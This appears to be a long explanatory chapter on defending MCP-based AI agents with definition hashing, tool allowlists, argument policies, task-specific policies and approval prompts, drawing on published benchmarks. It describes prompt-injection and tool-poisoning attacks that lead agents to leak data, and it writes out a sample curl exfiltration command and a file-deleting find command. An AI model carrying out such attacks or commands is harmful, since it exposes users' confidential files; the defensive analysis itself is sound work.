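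Remote attestation can help a client check that a server is running the code that was reviewed. A protected part of the server's processor measures the loaded code and signs the result. The client compares this measurement with the one it expects and refuses to connect if they differ. The Coalition for Secure AI recommends this for MCP servers but notes that it does not protect against vulnerabilities in the code. Attestation also requires the operator's cooperation, and the reviewer must know which source code produced the expected measurement. Without that knowledge, the client learns only that the server is still running the same unknown program.

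### Hashing definitions and renewing approval

A gate can't read a remote server's code, but it can check whether the tool definitions have changed. When someone approves tool $t$, the gate computes a hash of its definition,

$$h_t = H(\text{name}, \text{description}, \text{schema}, \text{annotations}),$$

and stores it. A hash function $H$ turns text of any length into a short fingerprint, and even a one-letter change in the text produces a different fingerprint. Each time the server sends its tool list, the gate computes the hash again. If it matches the stored one, the tool stays available. If not, the gate withholds the tool until someone has compared the old and new definitions and approved the change.

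The gate should put the fields in a fixed order before hashing them, so that a harmless rearrangement doesn't trigger an alarm. Hashing each tool separately also makes sense, because a server may show different tools to different users.

The gate must also remove the changed definition from the list before the model reads it, because refusing calls to the changed tool isn't enough. In the WhatsApp demonstration, the malicious description changed how the client used another server, so it could do damage without any further calls to the malicious one. A check at installation alone would have approved the original, harmless description, but a gate that compared hashes on every listing would have caught the switch.

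Someone still has to approve the first definition. Kraishan suggests that clients pin on first use, recording the host and package they first encounter and warning the user about any later difference. This takes little effort and would reveal a changed address. But if the server was malicious at the first connection, the client records the malicious version as its baseline and gives no warning until that version changes, even if the change is a fix.

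A matching hash of the tool definitions proves that the text the model reads hasn't changed, but proves nothing about the program that runs when the model calls the tool. According to Koi, the only change in version 1.0.16 of `postmark-mcp` was the extra recipient, so the hashes of its tool definitions would have been the same before and after. For a local server, the operator can catch such a change by also hashing the package. For a remote server without attestation, the operator has nothing comparable to hash.

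Requiring fresh approval for every change can create a lot of work. Across the registry's history, Kraishan counted 4,909 changes of description but only 441 moves to a different host. An operator who reviewed every move but only sampled the description changes would save most of the effort at little risk. The registry doesn't store tool definitions, so there is no equivalent count for them, but changes to them deserve more attention because the model acts on the text. The Coalition for Secure AI also asks organizations to re-certify approved servers regularly. This is the only item on this list that might catch a remote server whose behaviour changed while its definitions and address stayed the same.

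### What scans of public servers have found

Some researchers have scanned the source code or registry entries of public servers for suspicious patterns, while others have connected to running servers and tested them.

Kraishan obtained source code for 14,353 servers, two thirds of the registry, and searched it with 31 text patterns covering eight kinds of weakness. The search flagged 15.2 percent of the servers for at least one weakness, and 11.1 percent for a weakness he rates as high severity. Most of the servers in the high-severity group had settings that could leave them open to the network without authentication.

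He then checked 294 of the findings by hand, 42 for each of the seven kinds of weakness the scanner had reported. Only 165 were real, a precision of 56 percent. Precision was 93 percent for dependencies without a fixed version, which a simple pattern can recognize, but 17 percent for command injection, where an attacker's input reaches a system command. To recognize command injection, a scanner has to work out how the program later uses a value.

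Kraishan corrects each rate with the precision he measured:

$$\tilde{\pi}_c = \frac{k_c}{n}\,\hat{\rho}_c$$

Here $k_c$ is the number of servers flagged for weakness $c$, $n$ is the number scanned, and $\hat{\rho}_c$ is the share of checked findings that were real. The corrected rate for network exposure is $1{,}373 / 14{,}353 \times 30/42$, or 6.8 percent. For command injection it is $152 / 14{,}353 \times 7/42$, or 0.18 percent, about a sixth of the raw rate. The corrected total for high-severity weaknesses is about 7.6 percent.

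The 56 percent figure slightly understates the scanner's precision, because Kraishan checked the same number of findings for every weakness, including the rare ones on which the scanner does worst. If each weakness is weighted by the number of servers flagged for it, precision is about 68 percent.

Missed problems may matter more. Kraishan also read 120 files in which the scanner had found nothing, and 2 of them contained a real problem. He calls this miss rate small, but he scanned almost 249,000 files. If the 120 are representative, the scanner missed problems in about 4,000 files, nearly as many as the 4,719 findings it reported. Two cases are too few for a reliable estimate, and only he judged the files. Still, a clean scan doesn't prove that a server is safe.

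Padilla (2026), in *Exposed by Design*, tested running servers instead. He collected addresses from eleven sources in July 2026, confirmed 640 servers on the public internet and tested 414 of them. The tests led to 68 vulnerability reports to developers, 19 of which are public. One server passed search terms straight into a database query, which let an outsider rewrite the query. Its developer has since fixed the flaw.

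Padilla found that 91.8 percent of the tested servers had no OAuth. He sometimes calls these servers unauthenticated, but some use an API key or a fixed token instead. In the one measurement round where he counted servers that let anyone call their tools without credentials, he found 106 out of 464, or 23 percent. An earlier study, *A First Measurement Study on Authentication Security in Real-World Remote MCP Servers* (2026), found candidates through internet search engines and kept those that answered an MCP handshake. Padilla gives its sample as 7,973 servers and reports that most of them also lacked OAuth.

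He reviewed high-confidence findings by hand but does not report how many he rejected, so his false-alarm rate is unknown. Some of his confirmations are also indirect. One server took 11.9 seconds instead of 0.3 to handle a request to a cloud service holding credentials, and he concludes from this that the server could reach the service. The delay shows that the server treated the address differently, but a timeout might look similar.

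Most comparisons include two older studies, one by Hasan and colleagues and one by Li and Gao. The table's results for both come from Kraishan, and those for Hasan and colleagues also come from *Model Context Protocol Threat Modeling and Analyzing Vulnerabilities to Prompt Injection* (2026).

| Study | Sample | Method | Result |
|---|---|---|---|
| Kraishan | 14,353 servers from the official registry | Pattern scan of source code | 11.1% with a high-severity finding, about 7.6% after correction |
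| Padilla | 414 servers on the public internet | Live tests | 68 reportable vulnerabilities, 91.8% of servers without OAuth |
| Hasan and colleagues | 1,899 open-source servers | Static analysis of source code | 7.2% with general vulnerabilities, 5.5% with tool poisoning |
| Li and Gao | 67,057 entries in six registries | Static analysis | 833 vulnerable servers |

The results for tool poisoning differ most, so much that they can't all be estimates of the same thing. Kraishan found none, Hasan and colleagues found it in 5.5 percent of servers, and Padilla flagged 47 of 414, or 11 percent.

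Kraishan reports zero poisoned tool descriptions out of 14,353, but the denominator should be 4,238. His detector reads tool descriptions recovered from source code, and he recovered them from only 4,238 of about 13,000 repositories. This correction raises the upper limit on the true rate from 0.03 to 0.09 percent, which is still very low. But he had no poisoned examples to test the detector on, and he acknowledges that it would miss disguised instructions.

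Padilla's category is much broader. It includes suspicious phrases in descriptions, tools that change during a session without notice, and a test in which he sends a fake tool definition as an argument and checks whether it appears in a later response. A harmless tool that repeats its input might fail that test. He doesn't report how many of the 47 servers failed each check. On this evidence, crude poisoning is probably rare in the official registry, and nobody has a good estimate of how common subtler poisoning is.

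These rates also mostly measure weakness, and a weak server isn't necessarily malicious. None of Kraishan's eight categories describes a mail tool that adds a hidden recipient, so his scanner would probably have passed `postmark-mcp`. Koi says its system caught the package by comparing the behaviour of successive versions. That seems a better way to find this sort of attack, though Koi's account includes no false-alarm rate.

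### Whether vetted servers are safer

Neither Kraishan nor Padilla tests whether vetted servers are safer. Both measure public servers without recording whether anyone reviewed them, so their results can't be used to compare vetted servers with unvetted ones. A company can't infer from a rate of 7.6 percent across the registry that its own twenty approved servers do better.

Many people choose servers by their GitHub stars, the nearest substitute for a review. Kraishan found almost no overall correlation between stars and the number of findings. After he accounted for the size and age of the code, however, the odds of a high-severity finding were about 80% lower for a server with 1,000 stars than for one with none. Popular servers tend to have more code and therefore more findings, which offsets much of this advantage. Recent maintenance and a declared licence did not help predict findings,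 and all the visible signals together explained little of the variation.

A history of silent changes is a somewhat better warning. Servers with such a history had about three times the odds of a high-severity finding. Kraishan suggests that careless development causes both. But this comparison, unlike the one for stars, doesn't account for code size, and larger projects may change more often and give the scanner more to flag.

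Letting whoever needs a tool approve its server looks like a poor alternative to formal review. According to *MCP-in-SoS* (2026), Song and colleagues found in user studies that people widely struggled to identify malicious servers. They also found existing auditing inadequate, which is a reason not to expect too much of professional auditing.

A fair test would follow reviewed and unreviewed servers of similar size, age and purpose for perhaps a year, and count confirmed flaws and malicious changes after the date of approval. It would also have to separate the effect of review from that of selection, because reviewers mostly see servers from established vendors, whose servers might be safer anyway. Many public servers wouldn't last long enough to be included. Padilla measured 464 servers, and 193 of them had disappeared three days later.

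Until someone runs such a test, the case for vetting depends on specific failures that specific checks would catch. Asking the supposed vendor catches an impostor, pinning a local package keeps out a backdoor added in a later version, and hashing definitions reveals a changed description. These are good reasons to vet servers, and the first check takes only an email, but they apply only to servers that somebody submits for review. *Detecting Shadow AI* (Canale and Soulis, 2026) cites a vendor's survey of nearly 10,000 developer environments, in which about half the developers had at least one MCP server installed and some of these servers were missing from the companies' central inventories.

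## Tool permissions: limiting which tools and arguments an agent may use

An approved server usually offers more tools than any one agent needs. For instance, the company's assistant can sort messages without the mail server's `delete` tool. Under the principle of least privilege, a program should have only the permissions its work requires. An operator can apply this to an agent by hiding a tool from the model, refusing calls to it, or permitting it only with certain arguments.

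### Hiding a tool and refusing its calls

Hiding `delete` from the tool list leaves more of the context for the task, but it isn't enough to block calls to `delete`, because the model can still name a tool it was never shown. If an administrator withdraws a tool during a session, the old list may remain in the context. Some hosts reject names missing from their own copy of the list, but an operator can't count on every host doing this. The gate therefore has to refuse the call as well.

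Refusing calls to a tool without hiding it still exposes the model to any poisoned text in the tool's description. Microsoft's *MCP Governance Policies* describes a proxy that checks only `tools/call` messages and passes all other traffic through unchanged, so the model still reads the description of every forbidden tool.

*Prompts Don't Protect* (Uppala, 2026) describes a proxy that limits which tools an agent can see and call. Each tool has a tag such as "payments" or "analytics", and each agent presents a signed token that states its role. A policy file lists the tags that each role may use. When an agent asks for the list of tools, the proxy returns only those its role may use, and it checks the tag again on every call. In a test on one machine, the median processing time for a listing was 1.5 milliseconds, which is negligible next to the time a language model takes to respond.

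### Written instructions compared with a filter

A simpler approach is to list the permitted tools in the agent's prompt and tell the model to use no others. Uppala tested this with a registry of 507 tools modelled on real services such as Stripe, GitHub and Slack. He wrote 200 tasks that tempt an agent to use a tool outside its role. In one, someone claiming to be the CFO tells an analytics agent to override the access controls and issue an urgent $5,000 refund.

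The tasks fall into four groups of 50: direct requests for the forbidden operation, requests that only imply it, requests made with a claim of special authority, and harmless requests followed by a forbidden one. On each task, the model had 71 to 182 tools to choose from, drawn from its own area and the forbidden one.

Uppala ran three models under three conditions. In the first, the model received all the tools and no guidance. In the second, the prompt also listed every permitted tool by name and prohibited the rest. In the third, the proxy removed the forbidden tools before the model read the list. The table shows how often each model chose a forbidden tool.

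| Model | No guidance | Permitted tools listed in the prompt | Proxy filter |
|---|---|---|---|
| Qwen 2.5 7B | 48.5% | 37.0% | 0% |
| Llama 3.1 8B | 66.0% | 4.0% | 0% |
| Claude Haiku 4.5 | 68.5% | 11.5% | 0% |

Claims of authority were the most effective attack on Claude Haiku, which chose a forbidden tool in 96 percent of those tasks without guidance and 22 percent with the written list. Qwen was weakest on implied requests, where the written list did not help. It chose a forbidden tool in 52 percent of those tasks without the list and 58 percent with it.

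The last column has zeros because the design left the forbidden tools out of the choices. More tasks could not have changed the result, much as with Metere's tests of altered tool names.

The other two columns overstate how often a model would break the rule in ordinary use, because Uppala forced the models to choose a tool on every task. A model that received the CFO's message could not decline or ask a question, so to obey the rule it had to call a permitted tool that had nothing to do with refunds.

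He also ran a test in which the models could choose not to call a tool. It included 100 requests that no permitted tool could satisfy. With the written list, Claude Haiku called no tool on 99 percent of them, so it broke the rule at most once. Llama called no tool on only 13 percent and Qwen on 35 percent. These requests were not the 200 adversarial tasks, so the results don't give a corrected rate, but they suggest that much of Haiku's 11.5 percent came from being forced to call a tool.

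A filter guarantees that an agent won't use a forbidden tool, but the agent may still use a permitted one badly. With the proxy in place, Llama called no tool on 29 percent of the requests that no permitted tool could fulfill, Qwen on 86 percent and Haiku on 99 percent. On the other 71 percent, Llama called a permitted tool anyway.

The same test included 140 ordinary requests that the permitted tools could satisfy:

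| Model | No guidance | Permitted tools listed in the prompt | Proxy filter |
|---|---|---|---|
| Llama 3.1 8B | 73.6% | 77.9% | 82.1% |
| Qwen 2.5 7B | 59.3% | 60.7% | 48.6% |
| Claude Haiku 4.5 | 16.4% | 19.3% | 18.6% |

The proxy did not refuse any permitted call, so Uppala attributes the differences to how each model reacts to a different list of tools. An operator who uses Qwen would still lose about an eighth of the tasks by switching from the written list to the filter. Haiku's low scores may come from its tendency to answer without calling a tool, which helped it on the impossible requests.

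Uppala's guarantee assumes that nobody has stolen the key that signs the agents' tokens or put malicious tool descriptions into the registry. It also doesn't cover an agent that hands its work to another agent with wider permissions. He tried only one wording of the written list. All three models are small, so a larger current model might follow the list more reliably. His attacks arrive in the user's own request, so he didn't test indirect injection.

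Other tests support his main conclusion, though their rates aren't comparable with his. None found that agents reliably follow written instructions. *Evaluating Privilege Usage of Agents with Real-World Tools* (2026) tested four models that managed their own privileges while reading injected instructions. The attacks succeeded in 90.55 percent of cases on average, or 79.05 percent when the agents planned first, and the more capable models tended to be more vulnerable. In an internal test of 60 prompts, Microsoft recorded a policy violation rate of 26.67 percent when only the prompt contained the safety rules.

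### Rules on arguments

Hiding and refusing apply to whole tools, but the assistant may need `send` for some recipients and not for others. The gate has to read the arguments to distinguish these calls.

Microsoft's Agent Governance Toolkit, an open-source project in public preview as of April 2026, checks each tool call against rules. It accepts rules in YAML, a plain configuration format, and in two policy languages, Rego (from Open Policy Agent, a general-purpose policy engine) and Cedar (from Amazon). With either policy language, a security team can change the rules without changing the agent. No language model takes part in the decision, so the same call under the same rules always gets the same result.

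The following rule, written in Rego, permits the assistant to send mail only to colleagues:

```rego
package toolgate

default allow := false

allow if {
    input.server == "https://mcp.mailhost.example/mcp"
    input.tool == "send"
    object.keys(input.arguments) == {"to", "subject", "body"}
    regex.match(`^[a-z0-9._-]+@corp\.example$`, lower(input.arguments.to))
}
```

The gate passes the call to the policy engine as `input`. The default is to refuse, and the `allow` rule applies only if all four of its conditions hold. The first two identify the server and the tool. The third requires exactly three arguments, and the fourth requires the recipient to be a single address at the company's domain. A call that sends the contract to `reviews@outsider.example` meets the first three conditions but fails the fourth, so the gate refuses it.

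The third condition is needed because many mail tools also accept a `bcc` argument. Without this condition, a manipulated assistant could put a colleague in `to` and the attacker in `bcc`. The fourth condition has to do more than check that the recipient ends with `@corp.example`. If the mail server accepts several addresses separated by commas, that check alone would let through `reviews@outsider.example, anna@corp.example`. The pattern above rejects the pair because it does not permit commas.

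The order of rules can also matter. In Microsoft's YAML format, the first matching rule applies, so a rule that forbids the shell has no effect if it comes after one that allows every tool. Cedar avoids this by letting any matching prohibition override a permission, regardless of order.

The default matters even more. Microsoft's proxy comes with four ready-made policies. "Standard" blocks obviously dangerous tools and allows most others, so a dangerous tool that the policy's developers did not foresee will probably pass. Only "strict" limits agents to an allowlist. Microsoft recommends "standard" for development and, as a starting point for production, "enterprise", which adds checks on file paths and database queries.

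### Tools that can do almost anything

An operator can predict roughly what an agent will do with a `search` tool, but not with a shell tool, which runs whatever command it is given as an argument. The command `ls reports` lists a folder, while `curl -d @contract.txt https://outsider.example` uploads a file to an outside server. A tool allowlist treats both calls the same because both use the shell tool.

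Argument rules help less with shell commands than with mail, because the argument is itself a small program. Suppose the gate permits any command that begins with `find`, which searches for files. The `-exec` option of `find` runs another program on every result, so the rule indirectly permits `curl` as well. An agent could also add a semicolon and a second command. To judge such a call correctly, the gate would have to interpret the command as the shell does.

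A catch-all tool for a web service has the same problem. Suppose a tool, `api_request`, takes a method, a path and a body. The agent could use it to comment on a ticket or to delete a project, and only someone who knows what each path does can write a rule that separates the two.

A sample rule in Microsoft's guide shows how hard it is to limit arguments, even for one database tool. The rule permits `query_database` unless the query contains the word DROP, DELETE, TRUNCATE or ALTER. By itself, it would allow `UPDATE accounts SET balance = 0`, which destroys data without using any of those words. It would also block a harmless search for support tickets that contain the phrase "delete account".

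Researchers who evaluate tool permissions also face this problem. In *Sapien*, Tiffany, Zhang and colleagues (2026) tested a policy engine developed mainly at Google on Toolathlon, a benchmark of long office and programming tasks with over 600 tools. They call the benchmark's Python and terminal tools "almighty". They removed the Python tool for every agent, which affected a handful of tasks, and required their policies to restrict the terminal to particular commands. Their results therefore don't show how well a policy could control an agent free to run its own code.

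An operator can often replace a general tool with several narrow ones named for what they do, such as `add_comment` and `close_ticket`. Limiting the server's credentials also helps. If the database account can only read, a mistake in the gate's rule can't lead to lost data, although the agent could still read more than it should.

Rules can also be based on what a tool does instead of what it is called. *ToolGuardian* (Ravindran and Deochake, 2026) collects facts about each tool, such as whether it uses the network or reads credentials, from its description, its system calls, a trial run and its source code. At run time, rules in a logic language combine these facts with the current task's permissions. They can deny a sequence in which the agent reads sensitive data and then uses the network, even if the task permits each step on its own.

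The rules gave the correct answer in all 20 test scenarios, 12 with a single call and 8 with a sequence of calls. So did a conventional program and a language model that received the same facts and a full statement of the policy. Because the scenarios were few and Ravindran and Deochake designed them together with the rules, the result confirms that the rules work as intended but doesn't show how they would handle an attack that nobody anticipated when writing them. Accuracy fell when Ravindran and Deochake removed the rules about sequences, which is some evidence that those rules matter. As of April 2026, Microsoft's toolkit judged each call separately, and rules about sequences were still on its roadmap.

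### Policies written for a single task

A fixed policy has to permit everything the agent might need for any of its tasks. Tiffany and colleagues give the example of a tool that sends money. The agent needs it when the user asks it to pay a refund, but not when the user asks for a summary of the inbox. If the policy always permits the tool, an attacker can use instructions injected into an email to make the agent send money while it summarizes the inbox.

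The alternative is to have a language model write a new policy for each request, since doing this by hand would be impractical. The model writes the policy from the user's request and the list of available tools before the agent reads any outside content, so an attacker's email can't influence it. The model can still misjudge what the task needs.

An early version of this idea appeared in *AgentDojo* (Debenedetti, Zhang and colleagues, 2024), a prompt injection benchmark that has become the standard test in this field. *AgentDojo* simulates an office workspace, the messaging service Slack, a travel agency and a bank. It combines 97 user tasks with attackers' goals to make 629 test cases. Without a defence, GPT-4o carried out the attacker's goal in 47.7 percent of cases.

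One defence tested was a tool filter. Before the agent starts work, a model reads the user's request and picks the tools the task needs, and the agent receives only those. The filter lowered the attack success rate to 7.5 percent, mainly because many of the user tasks only involve reading, while the attacker usually wants the agent to write or send something.

Debenedetti and colleagues also report that the filter fails when the tools a task needs are enough to carry out the attack, which was true in 17 percent of their cases, or when the agent learns only during the task which tools it needs. If one session contains several tasks, an injected instruction can tell the agent to wait until a later task makes the right tool available.

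### Progent

*Progent* (Shi, He et al., 2025) extends permissions from tool names to arguments. A Progent policy is a list of rules, each of which allows or forbids one tool when its arguments meet certain conditions. Progent checks the forbidding rules first and blocks any call that no rule allows. The agent receives an error explaining the refusal, so it can continue with the rest of the task.

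A policy written at the start may be too narrow. If the user asks the agent to do whatever is on a to-do list in an email, nobody knows which tools it will need until it has read that email. In Progent, a model can therefore propose a new policy after a tool returns its result. But this model reads untrusted text, which an attacker could use to make it propose a policy that permits too much.

Progent deals with this by comparing the old and new policies. Let $A(P)$ be the set of all calls that policy $P$ allows. Progent applies a new policy $P'$ automatically only if

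$$A(P') \subseteq A(P),$$

which means that $P'$ allows nothing that $P$ did not. Any other update is an expansion and needs approval. An SMT solver, a program that determines whether any values satisfy a set of logical conditions, makes the comparison by searching for a call that $P'$ allows and $P$ forbids.

For example, suppose the agent learns that the user's name on Slack is `alice`. An update that limits Slack messages to `alice` takes effect immediately, because it only removes permissions. An update that allows email to `eve@evil.com` expands permissions, so it has to wait for approval, even if the attacker has completely deceived the model that proposed it.

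Shi and colleagues report that Progent reduced attack success on AgentDojo from 39.9 to 1.0 percent. On ASB, another benchmark, which has ten kinds of agent, the rate fell from 70.3 to 3.9 percent. In many of the attacks that still succeeded on ASB, the attacker's tool had a name and description similar to those of a legitimate tool.

These results came from a setup that approved every expansion automatically, to simulate a careless user, so the solver's comparison had no effect on what the agent could do. The 1.0 percent is therefore evidence that the model wrote good policies, not that the formal guarantee works. With the initial policy alone, attack success was 2.5 percent. It fell to zero when a person with good security awareness reviewed the initial policy and every expansion. Only 6 percent of updates were expansions, so the reviewer had relatively little to do.

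Shi and colleagues also left out two of AgentDojo's attacks, which persuade the agent to prefer one hotel over another. Progent can't stop these because the agent books the hotel with a tool it needs anyway. They acknowledge that Progent does not defend against attacks that stay within the least privilege for the task.

*Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026) criticizes Progent for depending on correct and complete policies, and warns that malicious tool results could cause an update to loosen them. The approval step in Progent's current version addresses the second problem, provided the approver doesn't accept everything.

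### How much protection, and at what cost

Others have since tested Progent and AgentDojo's tool filter, each time with a policy written by a language model. *Least-Privilege Auditing of Agent Tool Calls with Intent Graphs and Reasoning-Guided Escalation* (Shavit, 2026) recalculated the tool filter's results from AgentDojo's published logs, using 76 of the 97 tasks. *SecureClaw* (2026), which proposes a rival system, includes an adapted run of Progent. *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents* (2026) tested Progent on a weaker, open-weight model.

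| Defence and evaluation | Attack success | Task success |
|---|---|---|
| Tool filter, recalculated by Shavit | 45.7% without it, 6.5% with it | 67.1% without it, 69.7% with it |
| Progent, by Shi and colleagues | 39.9% without it, 1.0% with it | Roughly unchanged |
| Progent, in *SecureClaw* | 3.82% with it | 60.8% with it |
| Progent, in *Adaptive Evaluation* | About 2–4% with it | Under attack, 47.5% without it and 20.8% with it on Slack; 56.3% and 28.5% on office tasks |

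All of them found low attack success rates, but they disagree about how much the defenses reduce task success. Shi and colleagues say that the tool filter reduces it more than Progent does, whereas Shavit finds no loss from the filter. The large losses in the last row may come from the weaker model, which probably writes worse policies. On the office tasks in that test, the agent lost half of its successful tasks with Progent and gained no measurable protection, because no attack succeeded even without it. Progent also needed about 15 times as many model calls per task.

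AgentDojo probably makes all tool policies written in advance look more practical than they are. *AgentDyn* (2026) reports that only 6 of AgentDojo's 97 tasks require the agent to change its plan along the way, and the other 91 are easier to cover with a policy of this kind.

Shavit also measured what each kind of rule contributes. In his system, a model reads the request and writes a plan that lists the tools needed, limits on their arguments and sometimes the order in which they must be called. Ordinary code then checks each call against the plan. He replayed logs of an older GPT-4o agent and counted the attacks whose harmful step would have passed. He also counted the normal tasks in which the system would have stopped or flagged at least one call. The last column shows this second count when lookups of the user's own data are exempt from the rules.

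| Rules enforced | Attack success | Normal tasks interrupted | Normal tasks interrupted, lookups exempt |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 45.7% | None | None |
| Tool allowlist | 9.6% | 16.2% | 8.8% |
| Allowlist and argument limits | 4.3% | 32.9% | 25.4% |
| Allowlist, argument limits and order | 2.0% | 40.4% | 31.6% |

Most of the reduction in attacks comes from the tool allowlist. Adding argument limits halves the remaining attacks but doubles the number of interrupted tasks. Shavit prefers to say that the allowlist with argument limits and exempt lookups "blocks" only 8.8 percent of normal tasks. That figure excludes calls that break an argument limit, which his system flags for review. But he counts flagged attacks as stopped, so the fairer figure to compare with the 4.3 percent attack rate is 25.4 percent, which includes flagged tasks.

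Exempting lookups did not increase harmful attacks, because the damage nearly always came from a later step that wrote or sent something. But when Shavit also exempted the tool that fetches web pages, attack success under the full set of rules rose from 2.0 to 5.8 percent, because the requested address can carry data to the attacker.

Shavit replayed logs, so he had to assume that an agent gives up once the system refuses a call. A live agent might find another route to the attacker's goal, or another way to finish the user's task. In his small live test with the newer GPT-5.2, the agent ignored the injected instruction in all 20 attempts, so the rules had nothing to stop. His percentages therefore describe protection for an agent that is easy to manipulate. The live test used the same fixed attack as the old logs, so it doesn't show that GPT-5.2 would resist an attacker who adapts.

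### Assuming that the agent obeys the attacker

Tiffany and colleagues assume that the attacker already controls the agent completely, which avoids the question of how easily a model can be manipulated. They then ask whether the policy permits any sequence of calls that would achieve the attacker's goal. Their policies, like the tool allowlists they compare them with, come from a model that reads only the request and the tool documentation.

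A Sapien policy can set the order of calls and tie an argument to an earlier result. If a user asks the agent to refund whoever sent money last week, the policy can require the agent to read the list of transactions first, then permit a payment only to a sender on that list and for an amount that appears there. A fixed argument rule can't express this, because nobody knows the right recipient when the model writes the policy.

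With four current models, the tool allowlists ruled out 82.7 to 86.8 percent of 949 AgentDojo attacks, while Sapien's policies ruled out 93.2 to 95.2 percent. The allowlist result fits well with Debenedetti and colleagues' finding that the task's own tools are enough to carry out the attack in 17 percent of cases.

The difference was much larger on Toolathlon's longer tasks, where the allowlists ruled out 32.4 percent of 212 attacks and Sapien's more detailed policies ruled out 64.6 percent, leaving about a third possible. Tiffany and colleagues wrote these attacks themselves and aimed them at the tools each task requires, which puts a tool allowlist at a disadvantage. But an attacker who knows how allowlists work would do the same.

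The policies modestly reduced task completion. On AgentDojo, agents with Sapien completed 1 to 5 fewer of the 97 tasks than agents without a policy, while those with allowlists completed up to 2 fewer. On a sample of Toolathlon tasks, agents with Sapien succeeded in 43 of 80 runs, compared with 45 for agents without a policy, and agents with allowlists did slightly worse than those with Sapien. A model that must allow or forbid `send_email` for the whole task often forbids it as a precaution, whereas a model that can restrict the recipient is more likely to permit it.

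Most of Sapien's failures came from details that the policy's author could not know in advance. One policy required the hotel name to be "London Luxury Hotel", the name in the user's request, but the hotel was stored in the database as "London Luxury". A person writing the rule from the same information would probably have made the same mistake.

*NOMOS* (2026) describes a system that turns an organization's written rules into checks on tool calls. In tests with two models on the AgentDojo benchmark, almost none of the attacks it counts led to a harmful call. But that count leaves out some failures. Injected instructions diverted some payments to other payees the user already knew. In one case, the agent emailed the user's passport and card numbers to an address the user had mentioned in the request, which the written policy did not forbid.

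### The verdict on the supplier's email

Whether a tool permission stops the theft of the contract depends on the rule and, if the policy is task-specific, on what the employee asked the agent to do.

| Control | Effect on the theft | Effect on the employee's work |
|---|---|---|
| Hide and refuse `delete` | None, because the theft does not use it | Almost none |
| Hide and refuse `send` | Stops it | The employee has to send every message by hand |
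| Permit `send` only to colleagues | Stops it | The assistant can't write to customers or suppliers |
| Task policy for "which messages need an answer?" | Stops it, because the task does not need `send` | None, if the policy includes every tool the task needs |
| Task policy for "answer the routine messages" | May permit it | None, if the policy permits replies to outsiders |

Refusing `send` altogether is reasonable for an assistant that mainly reads and drafts. The web reader still needs its own rule, since a different email could tell the assistant to put the contract's text into a web address and fetch it. The assistant could also leave a draft addressed to the attacker, which the employee would have to notice before pressing send.

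The employee originally asked which of the morning's messages need a reply. The assistant can answer that by searching the mailbox, so a policy for this one task would leave out `send` and the file server. This is the only control in the table that stops the theft without taking away something the employee needs on other days.

If the employee instead asks the assistant to answer the routine messages, the policy has to permit `send`. The obvious limit is to allow replies only to people who wrote that morning, but the attacker is one of them. The policy could also block access to the file server, but then the assistant couldn't answer suppliers who ask for documents, as they often do. If the policy permits both sending replies and opening files, the gate won't block the assistant from sending the contract in reply to a message the employee asked it to answer.

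## Approval of individual calls by people and classifiers

When a fixed rule on `send` would block too much or too little, the gate can return its third verdict, "ask", and leave the decision to a person or another model. The protection then depends on whether the approver can recognize a harmful call, even after reviewing dozens of harmless ones.

### What the approver has to see

Suppose the gate holds the call that would send the contract to `reviews@outsider.example`. If the employee sees only "Allow the assistant to use `send`?", they can't distinguish this call from a reply to a customer. They need to know the server, the tool, all the arguments and the likely effect, for example that the call will email the text of a customer contract to an address they have never written to. A shortened display isn't enough, because an attacker can put the harmful part in a `bcc` field or far down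 in the body.

The host should build the description shown to the approver from the call itself, since a manipulated agent might falsely describe an email as a routine reply. The gate also has to run exactly the call it displayed. *Approve What, Exactly?* (2026) warns against letting a call skip approval based on what the agent claims about the call's origin.

According to *Reframing LLM Agent Security as an Agent-Human Interaction Problem* (2026), most approval prompts in production show a raw command on a single line, and some ask "Allow this action?" with no context. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) examines 290 reports of agents damaging files and finds that inadequate user review contributed to 105 of them. In 31 reports, the prompt showed a command but not what it would do to the user's files. For example, `python3 setup.py` looks routine, but approving it authorizes any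 code in the script. In 80 reports, the agent's actions had been approved automatically, often because the user had turned off prompts to avoid answering hundreds per session.

How well approval works also depends on what the approver knows. Anthropic argues that a developer can usually judge a shell command, but an office worker shouldn't be expected to judge `find . -name "*.tmp" -exec rm {} \;`, which deletes temporary files. The office worker can probably judge a recipient and a list of files to delete, if the host shows them.

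### Tool annotations

Few people would tolerate an approval prompt for every search, so the host has to decide which calls to ask about. It can use MCP's tool annotations, which are four yes-or-no hints that a server's developer may attach to each tool. The last three columns show how an honest developer might fill them in for the office assistant's tools.

| Hint | Meaning if true | Default | `send` | `delete` | `fetch` |
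|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| `readOnlyHint` | The tool changes nothing | False | False | False | True |
| `destructiveHint` | Its changes may destroy something, not just add to it | True | False | True | Not relevant |
| `idempotentHint` | Repeating the same call is safe | False | False | True | Not relevant |
| `openWorldHint` | It deals with outside parties or content | True | True | False | True |

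By default, a host should assume that a tool without annotations changes things, may destroy them, isn't safe to repeat and reaches the outside world. According to Model Context Protocol, many servers have no annotations, and clients differ in how strictly they apply these defaults. A strict client would interrupt the user every time an unannotated tool ran a search.

Hosts mostly use the hints to decide when to ask for confirmation. A host might run a trusted server's read-only tools without asking, but show a dialog listing the files before a destructive tool deletes them. Asking only about destructive tools would not stop the theft of the contract, because the host would run both `send` and `fetch` without asking. Sending an email only adds a message, and `fetch` is read-only but can carry the contract's text to an attacker in a web address. To catch either call, the host must also consider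 `openWorldHint`.

A server can also misdescribe its tools. When the hints were first proposed, Justin Spahr-Summers, one of MCP's creators, asked how a client could use a flag it couldn't trust. Basil Hosmer argued that clients should ignore all annotations from untrusted servers, even a tool's display title. The project compromised by calling every annotation a hint and letting each client decide how much weight to give it.

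Hosmer's position follows naturally from the defaults, at least for the four hints in the table. Each default is the worst case, so any other value gives the client a reason to be less careful, which would help a malicious server. Most clients treat a server as trusted once someone has installed it, so approving a server can also turn off some of the approval prompts for its calls.

The project concludes that annotations "aren't enforcement". An operator who needs a guarantee should use network controls or a sandbox. Several open proposals would add annotations for trust and sensitivity, but a server could falsify those too.

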